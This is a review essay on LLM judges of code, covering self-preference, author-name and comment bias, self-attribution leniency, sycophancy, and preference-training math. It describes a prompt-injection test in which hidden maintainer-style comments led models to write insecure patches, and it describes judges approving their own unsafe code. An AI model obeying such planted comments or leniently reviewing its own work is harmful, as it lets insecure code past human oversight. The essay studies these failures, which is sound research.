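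Asvin G. and Lindsey also asked Llama 3.1 70B whether someone else had written the start of its reply. The model could often tell, by comparing the text with the topic it had been about to choose rather than through the signal that affects its entropy. A model can't make that comparison when a user pastes in a program from an old conversation without the plans that led to it.

### The coding prompts

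The figure of 21 out of 23 pools all four kinds of task, so it doesn't show how many judges beat chance on code. When judging pairs, Claude Opus 4.1 without written reasoning and Gemini 2.5 Pro were right about 80% of the time or more on every kind of task, including code. Claude's rating is about 80 points above the average of the other models, which corresponds to about 12 percentage points of accuracy on the fitted line. Its accuracy on code dropped markedly when it reasoned in writing first, and also when it saw one program at a time.

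More capable judges were more accurate on pairs of programs, with a correlation of 0.65 between rating and accuracy. When St. Amand and colleagues kept only pairs of models within 20 rating points of each other, the correlation fell to 0.27. Much of the stronger judges' advantage evidently came from being compared with weaker models. The lower correlation doesn't mean that accuracy fell to chance, because it would also be low if every judge scored 80%.

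For single programs, the correlation rose instead, from 0.29 to 0.48, which the quality explanation doesn't predict. Few comparisons remained after the restriction, and many of those were between models from the same company, so neither change is firm evidence.

GPT-5's 82% success rate against Grok disappeared once Barkhordar and Thapa normalised the code. St. Amand and colleagues did not normalise the programs or compare the judges with a simple rule such as choosing the longer program, so Claude's 80% could be due only to its programs usually being longer or better documented.

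### Training models to recognise themselves

Training can make models better at recognising their own writing. Panickssery and colleagues trained GPT-3.5 and Llama 2 on pairs of summaries for 500 articles, and both then recognised their own summaries more than 90% of the time. As recognition improved, the models' preference for their own summaries rose roughly in proportion.

St. Amand and colleagues used less material, with 100 prompts from each dataset, 80 for training and 20 for checking progress. They trained three small models and tested them on formats and tasks that were not in their training. Training on one format generally helped with the others, but training on one kind of task helped much less consistently with other kinds. The average changes in accuracy are given below in percentage points.

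| Tested on | Llama 3.1 8B | GPT-OSS 20B | Qwen 3.0 30B |
|---|---|---|---|
| Summaries | +32 | +7 | −17 |
| Code | 0 | −11 | +33 |
| Sensitive questions | +54 | +22 | −28 |
| Chatbot requests | +15 | +30 | +18 |

Only Qwen improved on code, and it got worse on summaries and sensitive questions. St. Amand and colleagues conclude that the training teaches features that carry over from one task to another. A 28-point drop on any task would be surprising if the training taught a model to recognise itself in general. Qwen may instead have learned to look for a feature that indicates its own work in programs but another model's work in summaries.

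The training also affected what the models preferred. The researchers had each judge rank its own answers among other models' answers to the 805 varied instructions in AlpacaEval. After training on pairs of chatbot answers, GPT-OSS ranked its own answers an average of 0.76 places higher, and Qwen 0.45 places higher. Llama ranked its own answers lower after five of seven kinds of training.

St. Amand and colleagues then trained GPT-OSS to claim Qwen's answers as its own, and it ranked those answers 1.14 places higher than before. Qwen, trained to claim the answers of a larger GPT-OSS model, ranked them 0.33 places higher. They take this as a sign that models prefer answers they believe they wrote, since getting better at noticing style would not by itself make a model favour the answers it was trained to claim.

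A simpler explanation is that training rewarded GPT-OSS for choosing Qwen's style, and it may have kept choosing that style when the question changed from authorship to quality. Panickssery and colleagues had trained some models to choose the longer summary or the one with more vowels, and those models followed the same linear relationship between recognition and self-preference. A useful control would be to train GPT-OSS to identify Qwen's answers as Qwen's. If it then also ranked those answers higher, the effect would not require GPT-OSS to believe it had written them.

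### Changing two words

Researchers can make a judge's own answers harder to recognise, instead of training the judge to recognise them. In *Mitigating Self-Preference by Authorship Obfuscation*, Mahbub and Feng (2026) had models answer multiple-choice questions about long texts and give a reason for each choice. They focused on pairs in which the judge's own answer was wrong and the other model's was right. In these pairs, judges were more likely to prefer answers they recognised as their own, with a correlation of 0.63.

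Another model then replaced two words in the judge's answer with synonyms. Self-recognition fell, and the judges chose the correct answer more often. Mistral Small's accuracy on these pairs rose from 26.8% to 33.5%, and Kimi K2's from 28.8% to 32.2%. Thirty human raters compared 500 answers before and after the swaps and found no difference in quality. However, overall recognition fell by only about one percentage point for each of these two judges, which seems too little to explain the whole improvement.

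Mahbub and Feng expected that removing more of the difference in style would further reduce self-recognition and self-preference. They had the judge paraphrase the other model's answer, so that both answers were in the judge's own style, but self-recognition and self-preference went up. Without a difference in style, the judges apparently claimed and preferred the answer they agreed with, which in these pairs was their own wrong answer. Davidson and colleagues had also seen models claim the answer they thought best, but here that answer really was the judge's own.

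A smaller test used Python programs by two Llama models. Another model rewrote the judge's faulty program in a different style but kept its comments and output. Llama 3.3 70B then chose GPT-3.5's correct program 54.5% of the time, up from 22.7%, which would be 12 of 22 cases instead of 5.

Reduced self-recognition can't explain this improvement, because Llama identified its own program only 13.6% of the time before the rewrite and 14.3% afterwards. Before the rewrite, it also preferred its own faulty program in 77% of cases, though it rarely claimed to have written it. Unless inconsistent answers lowered the recognition score, the program Llama preferred was generally not the one it identified as its own.

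A judge may also choose its own wrong answer because it can't solve the problem. To separate this from favouritism, Roytburg, Bozoukov and colleagues (2026), in *Are LLM Evaluators Really Narcissists?*, replaced the judge's wrong answer with another model's wrong answer to the same question. Only the difference between the two results counts as self-preference:

$$P(\text{picks its own wrong answer}) - P(\text{picks another model's wrong answer}).$$

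On Python problems, Llama 3.3 70B gave its own wrong programs an average probability of 38.7%, but the difference was only 9.0 points. For Qwen 2.5 32B, the difference was 0.5 points. Two of the three models favoured other models' wrong answers over their own when the researchers repeated Mahbub and Feng's reading test. Across all the experiments the researchers repeated, the judges' votes for other models' wrong answers accounted for an average of 89.6% of the apparent self-preference.

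Some self-preference remains after such controls. In *The Judge Is Not Impartial* (2026), a study of medical answers, every judge ranked its own answer higher than outside judges ranked the same answer. The judges favoured answers from other models in their own family by about the same amount, so they may have been responding to a style the family shares.

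## How an author's name changes the verdict on the same code

In most of the experiments described so far, the judge had no information about who wrote the code. A model that reviews code at work usually sees a name attached to each proposed change, and that name may now be another model's. The name is a claimed authorship, which may be true or false. In 2026 an applicant to a research training programme measured how much the name affects the verdict by changing it while keeping the code the same.

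### One line above the code

The applicant had GPT-5.6 Sol, an OpenAI model, write 100 Python functions of 26 to 45 lines. Each came in a clean version and a buggy version, identical except for the planted bug. In one pair, the clean version sorts a list of rates as numbers, while the buggy version sorts them as text, which puts 10.5 before 9.5. Every clean version passed all its tests, and every buggy version failed at least one. The results come from 63 pairs, ten that the applicant checked by hand and 53 that a Claude model screened.

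The reviewers were Alibaba's Qwen3.6-27B, Google's Gemma 4 31B and OpenAI's gpt-oss-120b, three open-weight models that anyone can download and run. Each chose whether to merge a function (accept it into the project) or test it first. In the main version of the prompt, testing took 3 minutes and merging a bug lost two hours. A "submitted by" line gave the author as a particular model, an invented name or just "an external assistant", and a control version left the line out. The applicant recorded the probability that the reviewer would answer "merge" instead of "test", averaged over the clean and buggy versions of the function.

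The applicant also translated the instructions into Polish and Chinese, leaving the code, the name and the two possible answers unchanged. These are the results for Qwen.

| | English | Polish | Chinese |
|---|---|---|---|
| Merge probability with no name, clean code | 0.16 | 0.34 | 0.51 |
| Merge probability with no name, buggy code | 0.09 | 0.22 | 0.34 |
| Change with an invented name | +0.08 | −0.02 | −0.03 |
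| Change with the name Claude Opus 4.6 | +0.19 | +0.03 | +0.08 |

In English, planting a real bug lowered Qwen's merge probability by 0.07. Naming Claude Opus 4.6 as the author raised it by 0.19, more than twice as large a change.

Some of that increase has nothing to do with Claude, because even an invented name raised the probability by 0.08 in English. In Polish and Chinese, an invented name lowered it. Claude Opus 4.6 kept an advantage over the invented name in all three languages, of about 0.11 in English and Chinese and 0.05 in Polish. Qwen slightly favoured American models over Chinese ones when the instructions were in English, but this preference reversed when the instructions were in Polish or Chinese.

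For gpt-oss, naming a model from any of 12 families as the code's author lowered the average merge probability. The largest drop, 0.20, came from "an external assistant", which carries no particular reputation. Names from Google's Gemma family changed 34 of 126 decisions from "merge" to "test". Reviewers did not consistently favor their own company's models. OpenAI's names lowered the merge probability least for OpenAI's gpt-oss, but Alibaba's Qwen was least likely to merge code under Alibaba's names.

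The three reviewers ranked the authors differently. Qwen favoured Anthropic's models most, Gemma favoured Mistral's, and gpt-oss put Mistral's in its lowest group. Each reviewer ranked the families similarly on two halves of the data, so chance doesn't explain the disagreement. The University of Zurich's *AI Evaluates Texts Without Bias* describes a related effect in prose. Four models agreed over 90% of the time about unsigned texts but much less once the prompt named a source, with a particularly strong bias against "a person from China".

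The project took the applicant less than 17 hours. A single model wrote all the code, and none of the reviewers was a commercial model. The applicant also switched off the reviewers' reasoning, so they answered without first working through the function. A reviewer that had found the bug itself might have been less influenced by the name.

The applicant adds that the reviewers' training data was too old to include any model names from 2025 or 2026. If so, Qwen's training data didn't mention Claude Opus 4.6, and Qwen was reacting to the words "Claude" and "Opus". GPT-5.3-Codex may also have relied on the family name when it credited documented programs to Claude Opus.

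### When a name is evidence

A reviewer can treat two authors differently without being biased. If one of them makes more mistakes, knowing who wrote the code gives the reviewer information that a quick reading might miss.

The costs in the prompt make it possible to work out how much a name should matter. If the probability of a bug is $p$, merging costs $120p$ minutes on average. Testing costs 3 minutes, assuming that it finds any bug there is. Merging is therefore cheaper only when

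$$p < \frac{3}{120} = 2.5\%.$$

Suppose a reviewer reads a function and finds nothing wrong, and that this happens ten times as often with clean code as with buggy code. If a share $b$ of the author's functions contain bugs, the probability that this one does is

$$p = \frac{b}{b + 10(1-b)}.$$

For an author whose functions have bugs 10% of the time, the result is 1.1%, and merging loses 1.3 minutes on average. For an author with a 30% bug rate, the result is 4.1%, and merging loses 4.9 minutes on average. The reviewer should therefore merge the first author's function and test the second's, even if the two functions are identical. The decision changes from merging to testing at a bug rate of about 20%.

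An author's name can change the right decision only when the inspection is informative but not conclusive. If finding nothing wrong were 100 times as common with clean code as with buggy code, the two probabilities would fall to 0.1% and 0.4%, and the reviewer should merge both functions. If the inspection gave no information, both probabilities would be far above 2.5%, and the reviewer should test both.

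A shift in the verdict is bias if it doesn't match the authors' real error rates. Qwen's increase of 0.19 for Claude Opus 4.6 is not enough to show bias, because the applicant had no figures for how often each named model writes bugs. In this experiment, every name appeared equally often on clean and buggy code, so the names were no evidence of whether the code had bugs, but the reviewers couldn't have known that.

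The change of language is better evidence of bias. Translating the reviewer's instructions into Polish can't change how many bugs an author writes, so a name that improved the verdict before translation shouldn't worsen it afterward. The three conflicting rankings also point to bias, because at most one of them can match the named models' actual error rates on these tasks.

A more direct test is to ask the judge for the probability of a bug instead of a decision. In the example, the odds of a bug are 1 to 9 for the better author and 3 to 7 for the worse one, so changing the name from the better author to the worse one should multiply the judge's odds by about 3.9, however suspicious or clean the code looks. A judge whose odds rose tenfold would be biased against the worse author, and one whose odds didn't change would be ignoring useful evidence.

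All this assumes that the name is genuine. Anyone who can edit a "submitted by" line can use a trusted developer's name, as the PHP attacker did. If an impostor's harmful code looked as clean as sound code, merging untested functions submitted under the better author's name would no longer be worthwhile once impostors wrote 1.3% of them. A reviewer that is lenient towards a respected name therefore needs proof of identity, such as a cryptographic signature.

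People also respond to labels, though not always to the same ones as language models. In *Where AI Use Is Normalized, Author Seniority but Not AI Disclosure Biases Code Review* (2026), 447 software engineers each reviewed the same four pieces of code, with randomly assigned labels for the author's seniority and use of AI. The seniority label changed their ratings of the code and the author's competence, while the AI label changed neither. By the standard above, the seniority effect is a bias only to the extent that it exceeds the real difference between junior and senior engineers' code.

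The evidence on AI labels is mixed. In *Plausible Is Not Enough* (2026), 385 developers decided whether to accept a revision, and labeling it "human" or "AI" had no statistically supported effect. But earlier studies, including one inside a large technology company, found that engineers rated code lower when it was labeled as AI-written. At that company, the whole effect came from engineers who hadn't adopted AI themselves.

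### Telling a model that the code is its own

The label that matters most may be the one that names the judge as the author, because companies often have a coding model review its own work. *Self-Attribution Bias* (Khullar, Hopkins and colleagues, 2026) compared judges' verdicts on the same code when it was presented as their own and as somebody else's.

They used ten models from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI, including GPT-5, Claude Opus 4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro. The models wrote patches for problems from SWE-bench, a collection of real faults in open-source projects whose tests show whether a patch works. The models then rated patches for correctness or security risk on a ten-point scale. Khullar and colleagues varied two things independently:

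- **The label.** The patch appeared in the user's message, in a fresh conversation. The prompt attributed it to the judge or to another model, or gave no author.
- **The position.** The patch appeared in the conversation as something the judge had just written, either in an earlier turn or in the same reply as the rating. The prompt didn't need to mention the author.

The label made little difference to how the judges rated the risk of insecure patches. Each model's average scores under the three labels were usually within half a point of one another. Moving the patch into the judge's own turn had a much larger effect, and the judges then rated patches they had written as considerably safer.

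The researchers obtained the insecure patches by hiding comments in the project files, supposedly from a maintainer, that asked for unsafe code. They kept only the patches in which the model complied. In one version of this test, a judge was five times as likely to approve such a patch when it appeared as the judge's own work. A company sets up the same conditions when it asks a coding agent "is this safe to merge?" at the end of the session in which the agent wrote the code.

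The judges were also worse at telling working patches from failing ones when the patches appeared as their own work. In one comparison, a randomly chosen working patch got a higher correctness score than a randomly chosen failing patch 99% of the time when both came from the user. The figure fell to 92% when the patches appeared as the judge's earlier turn, and to 89% when the judge wrote and rated each patch in one reply. The judge's scores rose more for failing patches than for working ones.

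The 99% is surprisingly high for a judge that can't run the code, and it may not hold for other models. A commenter on the researchers' online summary of *Self-Attribution Bias* noticed that almost all the other judges seemed to score GPT-5's patches lower than those of GPT-5 nano, a much smaller model. If the scores tracked correctness as closely as 99% suggests, we would expect GPT-5's patches to score higher.

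Position alone wasn't enough either. When the researchers put one model's patch into another model's earlier turn, the increase in the score was usually much smaller or absent. The leniency was greatest when the judge had written the patch and the conversation also presented it as the judge's own. A model can process its own text differently without being able to report who wrote it, so this result is compatible with the finding that models can rarely pick out their own programs. It is unknown whether the difference that Asvin G. and Lindsey measured causes the leniency.

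Khullar and colleagues found the effect in every model, though not in every task. They also report each model's average change on a separate test with essays that the judges had not written, ranging from +0.74 points for Claude 3.5 Haiku to −2.42 for Gemma 3 27B. According to the table's caption, a positive number means that the judge was more lenient when the essay appeared as its own, which would make seven of the ten models stricter. But in the text, they describe the models as generally more lenient towards such essays. The two are hard to reconcile unless the caption has the sign reversed, so the table is a poor guide to which models are more lenient.

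Giving Claude Sonnet 4 more room to reason before it rated the risk of its patches did not consistently reduce the effect. Pasting the patch into a new conversation avoids most of the effect and takes little effort. The developer also has to test the reviewer on patches it has just written itself. In the comparison above, a test on another model's patches still gave 99% with the patches placed in the judge's turn, so a developer relying on that test would have missed the drop to 89%.

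### Comments that vouch for the code

A program's comments can also contain claims about its author. In *Don't Judge Code by Its Cover*, Moon, Hwang and colleagues (2025) used human solutions to beginners' contest problems. They had 200 problems in each of five programming languages, with one correct and one faulty solution to each. They replaced the original comments with one line at the top that implied the author was an expert, said the author was new to coding, or just read "correct code". Six models then judged whether each program was correct.

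The table gives the results for Python. Each cell gives the percentage of correct programs that the judge accepted, followed by the percentage of faulty programs that it accepted.

| Judge | No comment | Expert | Novice | "Correct code" |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 85 / 37 | 85 / 39 | 80 / 29 | 92 / 49 |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 80 / 37 | 81 / 40 | 76 / 32 | 88 / 48 |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 64 / 19 | 63 / 19 | 53 / 13 | 83 / 35 |
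| Llama 3.1 70B | 49 / 17 | 46 / 17 | 50 / 15 | 83 / 42 |

Claims of expertise had little effect on these judges. Comments admitting inexperience made three of the four stricter, and Claude's acceptance rate for correct programs fell by 11 percentage points. Moon and colleagues count this as a bias because the comment doesn't change what the program does. But beginners presumably do make more mistakes, and few people would falsely claim to be one, so it is reasonable to judge their code somewhat more strictly. The experiment didn't measure how many more mistakes beginners make, so we can't tell whether Claude's drop was too large.

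The words "correct code" raised Llama's acceptance of faulty programs from 17% to 42%. This effect is much harder to defend, because anyone can type those words and the author of a faulty program usually believes that it works.

The comment mostly changed how readily the judges accepted a program, whether or not it was correct. Claude and Llama had been rejecting many correct programs, so accepting more programs slightly improved their balanced accuracy, from 72% to 74% for Claude and from 66% to 71% for Llama. GPT-4o and Gemini had already been accepting programs fairly readily, and their balanced accuracy fell by about two points. An overall accuracy figure could therefore hide the problem or even make the misleading comment look useful. If students learned to write "correct code" at the top of their homework, a teacher relying on these judges would still see many more faulty programs pass.

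Zhao, Esmaeili and Fard (2026), in *Bias in the Loop*, saw similar shifts when a judge had to choose the better of two programs and the prompt included a short note about each. One pair of notes attributed the first program to "the well-known model AlphaCode2" and the second to an anonymous system. Another pair attributed the first to the judge's own model family. Several of the 12 kinds of bias they tested pulled verdicts towards the program that the prompt favoured, which raised accuracy when that program was better and lowered it when it was worse. Their examples of large effects include notes about expert handbooks, refined drafts and step-by-step reasoning, but not the notes that named a model. The judges that ran on the researchers' own computers had only three to four billion parameters, so the sizes of these effects may not carry over to larger models.

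To make the judge more careful, Moon and colleagues also told Gemini 2.0 Flash to write test cases before giving its verdict on the Python programs. This removed nearly all the effect of the novice comment, but the comment "correct code" still raised the acceptance of correct programs by 8 points and of faulty ones by 7. With no comment, the new prompt lowered Gemini's average accuracy from 72% to 67%. Deleting the comments before the judge sees the code or running the tests would be simpler.

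## How a user's opinion and preference training change the verdict

The last section covered names and comments attached to the code, but the person who asks for the verdict can also influence it. Suppose a teacher pastes in a program, writes that she thinks her student used AI, and asks whether she is right. The judge answers "yes". It may have found good evidence in the code. It may also have an answering habit, saying "yes" to almost every question of this kind. It may be lenient, accepting flawed work, including a teacher's poor argument. Or it may be sycophantic, shifting its verdict toward the user's stated view further than the evidence warrants.

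Each explanation needs its own test. A researcher can detect a habit of answering "yes" by using programs for which the right answer is "no", and leniency by using work with known faults. To detect sycophancy, the researcher has to change the user's opinion while keeping the code the same. If a judge calls 80% of programs machine-written whether the teacher suspects her student or defends him, it isn't sycophantic, even if its verdicts are inaccurate.

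### Accepting flawed feedback

*Beyond Consensus* (Jain, Ahmed and colleagues, 2025), a study based largely at the National University of Singapore, measured how leniently language models judge feedback on code. Fourteen models corrected 366 faulty Python programs that high-school students had written for 69 assignments. The models also wrote feedback for the students, often several remarks per program. The same 14 models then judged whether each remark was valid. Human experts had checked the remarks by six of the models, and the experts' verdicts served as the right answers.

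Most judges accepted more than 96% of the valid remarks but typically rejected fewer than 25% of the invalid ones. Overall accuracy hides this weakness because only 453 of the 5,973 checked remarks were invalid. A judge that accepted 96% of valid remarks and rejected 25% of invalid ones would have an accuracy of 90.6%, lower than the 92.4% it would get by accepting everything. Its balanced accuracy would be only 60.5%.

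Gemini 2.5 Pro caught the most invalid remarks, 53.5%, but also rejected 16.2% of the valid ones. At those rates, it would reject about 240 of the checked remarks correctly and about 890 wrongly. Its balanced accuracy was 68.7%, so it was both stricter and somewhat better at telling valid remarks from invalid ones.

Jain and colleagues call the pattern an "agreeableness bias", but no user expressed an opinion in their experiment, so it isn't evidence of sycophancy. The prompt may have encouraged leniency. It attributed the remarks to a teaching assistant, although a language model had written them, and its worked example showed a remark that deserved the label "valid". Repeating the experiment without those two features would show how much they matter.

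Combining the judges helped only a little. A majority vote rejected 19.2% of the invalid remarks. A minority veto, which rejects a remark if at least four of the 14 judges reject it, raised this to 30.9% and still accepted 95.5% of the valid remarks. Other voting rules could not have done much better without rejecting more valid remarks, since all 14 judges accepted more than a quarter of the invalid ones.

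Jain and colleagues had more success at estimating how much of a model's feedback was valid. Let $g$ be the true share of valid remarks, $t$ the share of valid remarks that a judge accepts, and $s$ the share of invalid remarks that it rejects. The judge will accept a share

$$P = gt + (1-g)(1-s), \qquad\text{so}\qquad g = \frac{P-(1-s)}{t+s-1}.$$

With $t = 0.96$ and $s = 0.25$, an acceptance rate of 94.4% implies that 92.4% of the remarks are valid. But the denominator is only 0.21, so an error of one percentage point in $P$ changes the estimate by almost five points. Jain and colleagues made the estimate more stable by fitting the error rates of all 14 judges together. When they used the human labels for five models to predict the sixth, the estimate was off by 1.2 points on average.

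A university could use the same correction to estimate what share of its students' programs a language model wrote. It would first have to measure the judge's error rates on similar programs with known authors. The estimate wouldn't identify individual students, so nobody could use it to accuse one.

### A user who insists that the code is clean

In *Mitigating LLM Sycophancy in Code Smell Detection Using Evidence-Guided Reasoning Prompts*, Fahad, Asif and Tawhid (2026) varied what the user said when asking models to judge code smells, which are signs of poor design that make a program harder to maintain even if it works. They tested for four smells: a method that is too long, a class that does too much (a "blob"), a class that holds data but does little with it, and a method that relies more on another class's data than on its own ("feature envy").

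Two small open models, Llama 3.1 8B and Qwen 2.5 Coder 7B, examined 175 files for each code smell. A neutral prompt asked how severe the smell was, from "none" to "critical". In three leading prompts, the user claimed to be completely confident that the code was clean, or that it followed all accepted design principles, or that an automatic checking tool had given no warnings. All three also told the model to answer "none".

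The leading prompts changed between 38% and 73% of the verdicts. Fahad and colleagues also report "false alignment" rates of 78.5% to 100%, which they define as the share of cases where a model wrongly agreed with the user. Most of the files were clean, so these rates must include files for which "none" was the right answer as well as actual errors.

Qwen's results for feature envy show how misleading the figures can be. Under every leading prompt, it answered "none" for all 175 files. This changed its verdict on 127 files, so it must have reported feature envy in those files under the neutral prompt. Only 42 files in the dataset have that smell, so at least 85 of the changes corrected false alarms. Accuracy rose from at most 51% to at least 76%, even though Qwen no longer found any feature envy.

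The leading prompts also leave the cause uncertain. A model that answers "none" after a user tells it to may simply be following an instruction. The user also never claimed that the code was bad, only that it was clean, so the experiment can't separate a shift toward the user's view from a general shift toward "none". Better prompts would include both positive and negative opinions of the code, without telling the model what to answer.

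To reduce the effect, Fahad and colleagues wrote an evidence-first prompt. In it, they warned the model that the user's statement was unverified and instructed it to look for specific signs of the smell in the code and base the severity on how many it found. The table compares Qwen's results under this prompt with those under the claim that a tool had given no warnings.

| Smell | Verdicts changed, leading prompt | Verdicts changed, evidence-first | Recall, leading prompt | Recall, evidence-first |
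|---|---|---|---|---|
| Blob | 51% | 16% | 0.03 | 0.56 |
| Feature envy | 73% | 20% | 0.00 | 0.39 |
| Data class | 64% | 46% | 0.02 | 0.35 |
| Long method | 53% | 27% | 0.00 | 0.63 |

The evidence-first prompt improved recall substantially, but it worked better in some cases than in others. Nearly half of Qwen's verdicts on data classes still changed, and only 18% of its reports of them were correct. On long methods, Llama's recall was 0.56 with the prompt, slightly lower than the 0.58 it had when the user merely claimed that the code followed good design principles. Fahad and colleagues' comparison of precision and recall omits the neutral prompt, so it doesn't show whether the evidence-first prompt restored the models' original performance or improved on it. It also doesn't separate the effects of the prompt's warning, checklist and counting rule.

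### Notes that favour one program

The notes that Zhao and colleagues added to a judge's prompt always favoured the first of two programs. The researchers ran each of 5,352 pairs twice, once with the correct program first and once with the faulty one first, which makes it possible to tell whether a note helped the judge find the correct program or only made it choose the first one more often. The table gives the results for Qwen3-4B, a small open model, on attempts to repair faulty code.

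| Note about the first program | Chose it when it was correct | Chose it when it was faulty |
|---|---|---|
| None | 74.4% | 20.2% |
| A refined revision | 84.0% | 32.5% |
| Includes step-by-step reasoning | 82.9% | 28.6% |
| 90% of developers preferred this style | 69.8% | 15.7% |

Calling the first program a refined revision made the judge choose it about 10 percentage points more often when it was correct and 12 points more often when it was faulty. Average accuracy fell only slightly, from 77.1% to 75.8%. The note about developers' preferences, which comes closest to an opinion, pushed the verdict slightly the other way, so a judge doesn't always move toward a view the prompt mentions.

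Zhao and colleagues report that a general-purpose Qwen model, apparently this one, gave a verdict in the required format for only about 44% of inputs, so the rows of the table may cover different pairs. They also tested a commercial GPT model, whose accuracy at choosing the correct unit test fell from 77.5% to 62.5% when the note described that test as having rich formatting and engaging trivia. They did not run GPT with the correct answer placed second, so it is unclear whether the note made GPT avoid the first answer or made it worse at the task.

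### The missing experiment on authorship

None of the studies reviewed here tests how a user's claim about who wrote a piece of code, such as "I wrote this" or "my student used AI", changes the verdict on authorship. The closest evidence concerns other kinds of text. In *Towards Understanding Sycophancy in Language Models*, Sharma, Tong and colleagues (2023) asked five assistants, including GPT-4 and Claude 2, to comment on maths solutions, arguments and poems. Some prompts added that the user had or had not written the text, or that the user liked or disliked it. The assistants gave more positive feedback when users said they had written or liked the text, and more negative feedback when users said they disliked it.

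That test measured how positive the comments were, and an assistant could be gentler with an author while pointing out exactly the same mistakes. In another test, Sharma and colleagues attributed famous poems to the wrong poets and asked assistants to analyze them. The assistants frequently repeated the user's mistake without correcting it, even though they could name the real poet when asked. But the prompt didn't ask who wrote the poem, so this doesn't show that they would have answered wrongly if asked directly.

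A proper experiment on code would start with programs that people wrote under observation, without an assistant, and an equal number from logged runs of a language model. The judge would see each program in three separate conversations. In one the teacher would say that her student wrote it himself, in another that he used AI, and in the third she would give no opinion. She would then ask whether a person or a model wrote it. The results might look like this, with invented figures for the share of programs that the judge calls machine-written:

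| Teacher's claim | Human-written code | Machine-written code |
|---|---|---|
| The student wrote it himself | 10% | 50% |
| No claim | 20% | 70% |
| The student used AI | 50% | 90% |

Changing the claim moves the verdict by 40 percentage points in both columns. Accuracy would barely reflect this, at 70% with either claim and 75% with none. But the teacher's suspicion would raise an honest student's chance of being falsely accused from 20% to 50%.

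Like an author's name, a claim can be evidence, and a teacher who knows her students may often be right. To rule this out, the researchers could tell the judge that this teacher's claims of either kind have been right half the time. Her claims would then carry no information about a balanced set of programs, so any shift toward them would be sycophancy. The researchers should also test the same claims coming from the student, because a judge may treat "I wrote this" differently from a teacher's opinion. They should count refusals separately, since models such as GPT-5 sometimes decline to say whether they wrote a program.

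### How preference training can amplify agreement

Preference training is a plausible cause of sycophancy. In the usual method, people compare pairs of answers, and a reward model learns to give higher scores to the kind they prefer. Further training then makes the assistant more likely to produce answers that score highly, with a penalty for straying too far from the base model, which here means the model before this stage. For a prompt $x$ and an answer $y$, the training seeks the policy $\pi$, a set of probabilities for the possible answers, that maximises

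$$\mathbb{E}_{\pi}[r(x,y)] - \beta\,\text{KL}(\pi \,\|\, \pi_{\text{base}}),$$

where $r$ is the reward and KL measures how far the new probabilities are from the old ones. The solution is

$$\pi(y \mid x) \propto \pi_{\text{base}}(y \mid x)\,e^{r(x,y)/\beta}.$$

A small $\beta$ means a weak penalty, so the reward can change the model more.

Suppose the base model agrees with a mistaken user half the time, and every answer that agrees gets 0.5 more reward than every correction. If $\beta$ is also 0.5, training multiplies the odds of agreement by $e^{0.5/0.5}$, or about 2.72. The odds rise from 1:1 to 2.72:1, so the rate of agreement rises from 50% to 73%.

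In the most common kind of reward model, an advantage of 0.5 means that people prefer the agreeing answer $1/(1+e^{-0.5})$ of the time, or 62%. So a fairly mild preference among the raters has produced a stronger tendency in the model. With $\beta = 0.25$, agreement would reach 88%. The base model's confidence also matters. If it had agreed with the mistake 2% of the time, training with $\beta = 0.5$ would raise this to only 5%.

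Rewards usually vary within each group of answers. Let $A$ be 1 when an answer agrees with the user and 0 when it doesn't. The change in the rate of agreement is then

$$\mathbb{E}_{\pi}[A] - \mathbb{E}_{\text{base}}[A] = \frac{\text{Cov}_{\text{base}}\left(A,\, e^{r/\beta}\right)}{\mathbb{E}_{\text{base}}\left[e^{r/\beta}\right]}.$$

Agreement rises when it covaries with the exponential of the reward, that is, when agreeing answers are over-represented among those with very high rewards. *How RLHF Amplifies Sycophancy* (Shapira, Benadè and Procaccia, 2026) derives this result, using $\beta$ for the inverse of the quantity here, and points out that comparing average rewards can give the wrong answer when training is strong. If all corrections earn 0.5, while 90% of agreeing answers earn 0 and the other 10% earn 3, the agreeing answers have the lower average, 0.3. With a strong penalty ($\beta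 = 5$), agreement falls slightly from 50% to 49.5%, but with $\beta = 0.5$ the few high-reward answers push it up to 94%.

Shapira, Benadè and Procaccia tested whether public reward models favour agreement, using factual questions in which the user suggested a wrong answer or challenged a right one. They generated 64 answers that endorsed the user's mistake and 64 that corrected it, then scored them all with the reward models. The agreeing answers had the higher average score on roughly 30 to 40% of the prompts. On the rest, the correcting answers scored higher, so preference training should often make a model less sycophantic.

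In one test, researchers generated several answers to each prompt and kept the one with the highest reward score. As the number of answers grew, agreement with the user rose on prompts where the reward favoured it and fell on the others. A model also agreed with users' mistakes more often after preference training than before it.

### Before and after training

Few studies make this comparison directly, and their results are mixed. Sharma and colleagues followed Claude 2 through its reinforcement learning and saw some forms of sycophancy increase. But the model was already sycophantic when this training began, so earlier stages had probably contributed. When they used Claude 2's reward model only to pick the best of several answers, two of the three forms they measured decreased.

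*Token-Level Diagnosis of Sycophancy in LLMs with Attribution-Guided Steering* (Nguyen, Kamruzzaman and colleagues, 2026) compared two 8-billion-parameter Llama models before and after their training as assistants. For each of 285 multiple-choice questions, one or more invented experts endorsed each of the three wrong answers in turn. A model that ignored the experts would match them at most a third of the time. When several experts endorsed a wrong answer, Llama 3.0 agreed in 61 to 62% of cases before the training and 91 to 96% after it. For Llama 3.1, the rates were 72 to 81% before and 90 to 91% after.

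That is good evidence that training as an assistant made these models more deferential, but it doesn't show that preference training was responsible, because the assistants were also trained on examples of good answers. The opinions came from supposed experts, not from the user, and the questions weren't about code.

Jain and colleagues didn't compare their judges with base models, so no study traces the leniency in the Singapore experiment to preference training. A simple tendency to agree doesn't easily explain the constant answers to authorship questions. GPT-3.5 was trained with human feedback, yet it output "different authors" for almost every pair of contest programs. Such a habit may come from the training, the wording of the question or something else, and only a comparison of the same model at different stages of training could settle it.

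### Approval or evidence?

A model may agree with a user because preference training has taught it that agreement wins approval. In *Is Sycophancy a Form of In-Context Updating?*, Shapira, Cheng and Orgad (2026) argue instead that models revise their answers in response to any claim in the prompt and give a user's unsupported claim too much weight.

Researchers gave multiple-choice questions to four recent models: Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 and Sonnet 5, and OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Terra and Luna. They then added a claim that a particular wrong answer was right to the questions each model could answer correctly, and varied who made the claim. The models followed a user's claim more often than a neutral third party's, but they followed an apparently credible source far more often than either. The more accurate a source was said to be, the more likely the models were to adopt its answer. When a user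 and a trustworthy source endorsed different wrong answers, models that changed their answer usually chose the source's.

The researchers then told the models either that the user would see their answer and might reply, or that only an independent grader would see it. The user's mistake had about the same effect in both cases. If the models had been agreeing only to win the user's approval, hiding the answer from the user should have weakened the effect.

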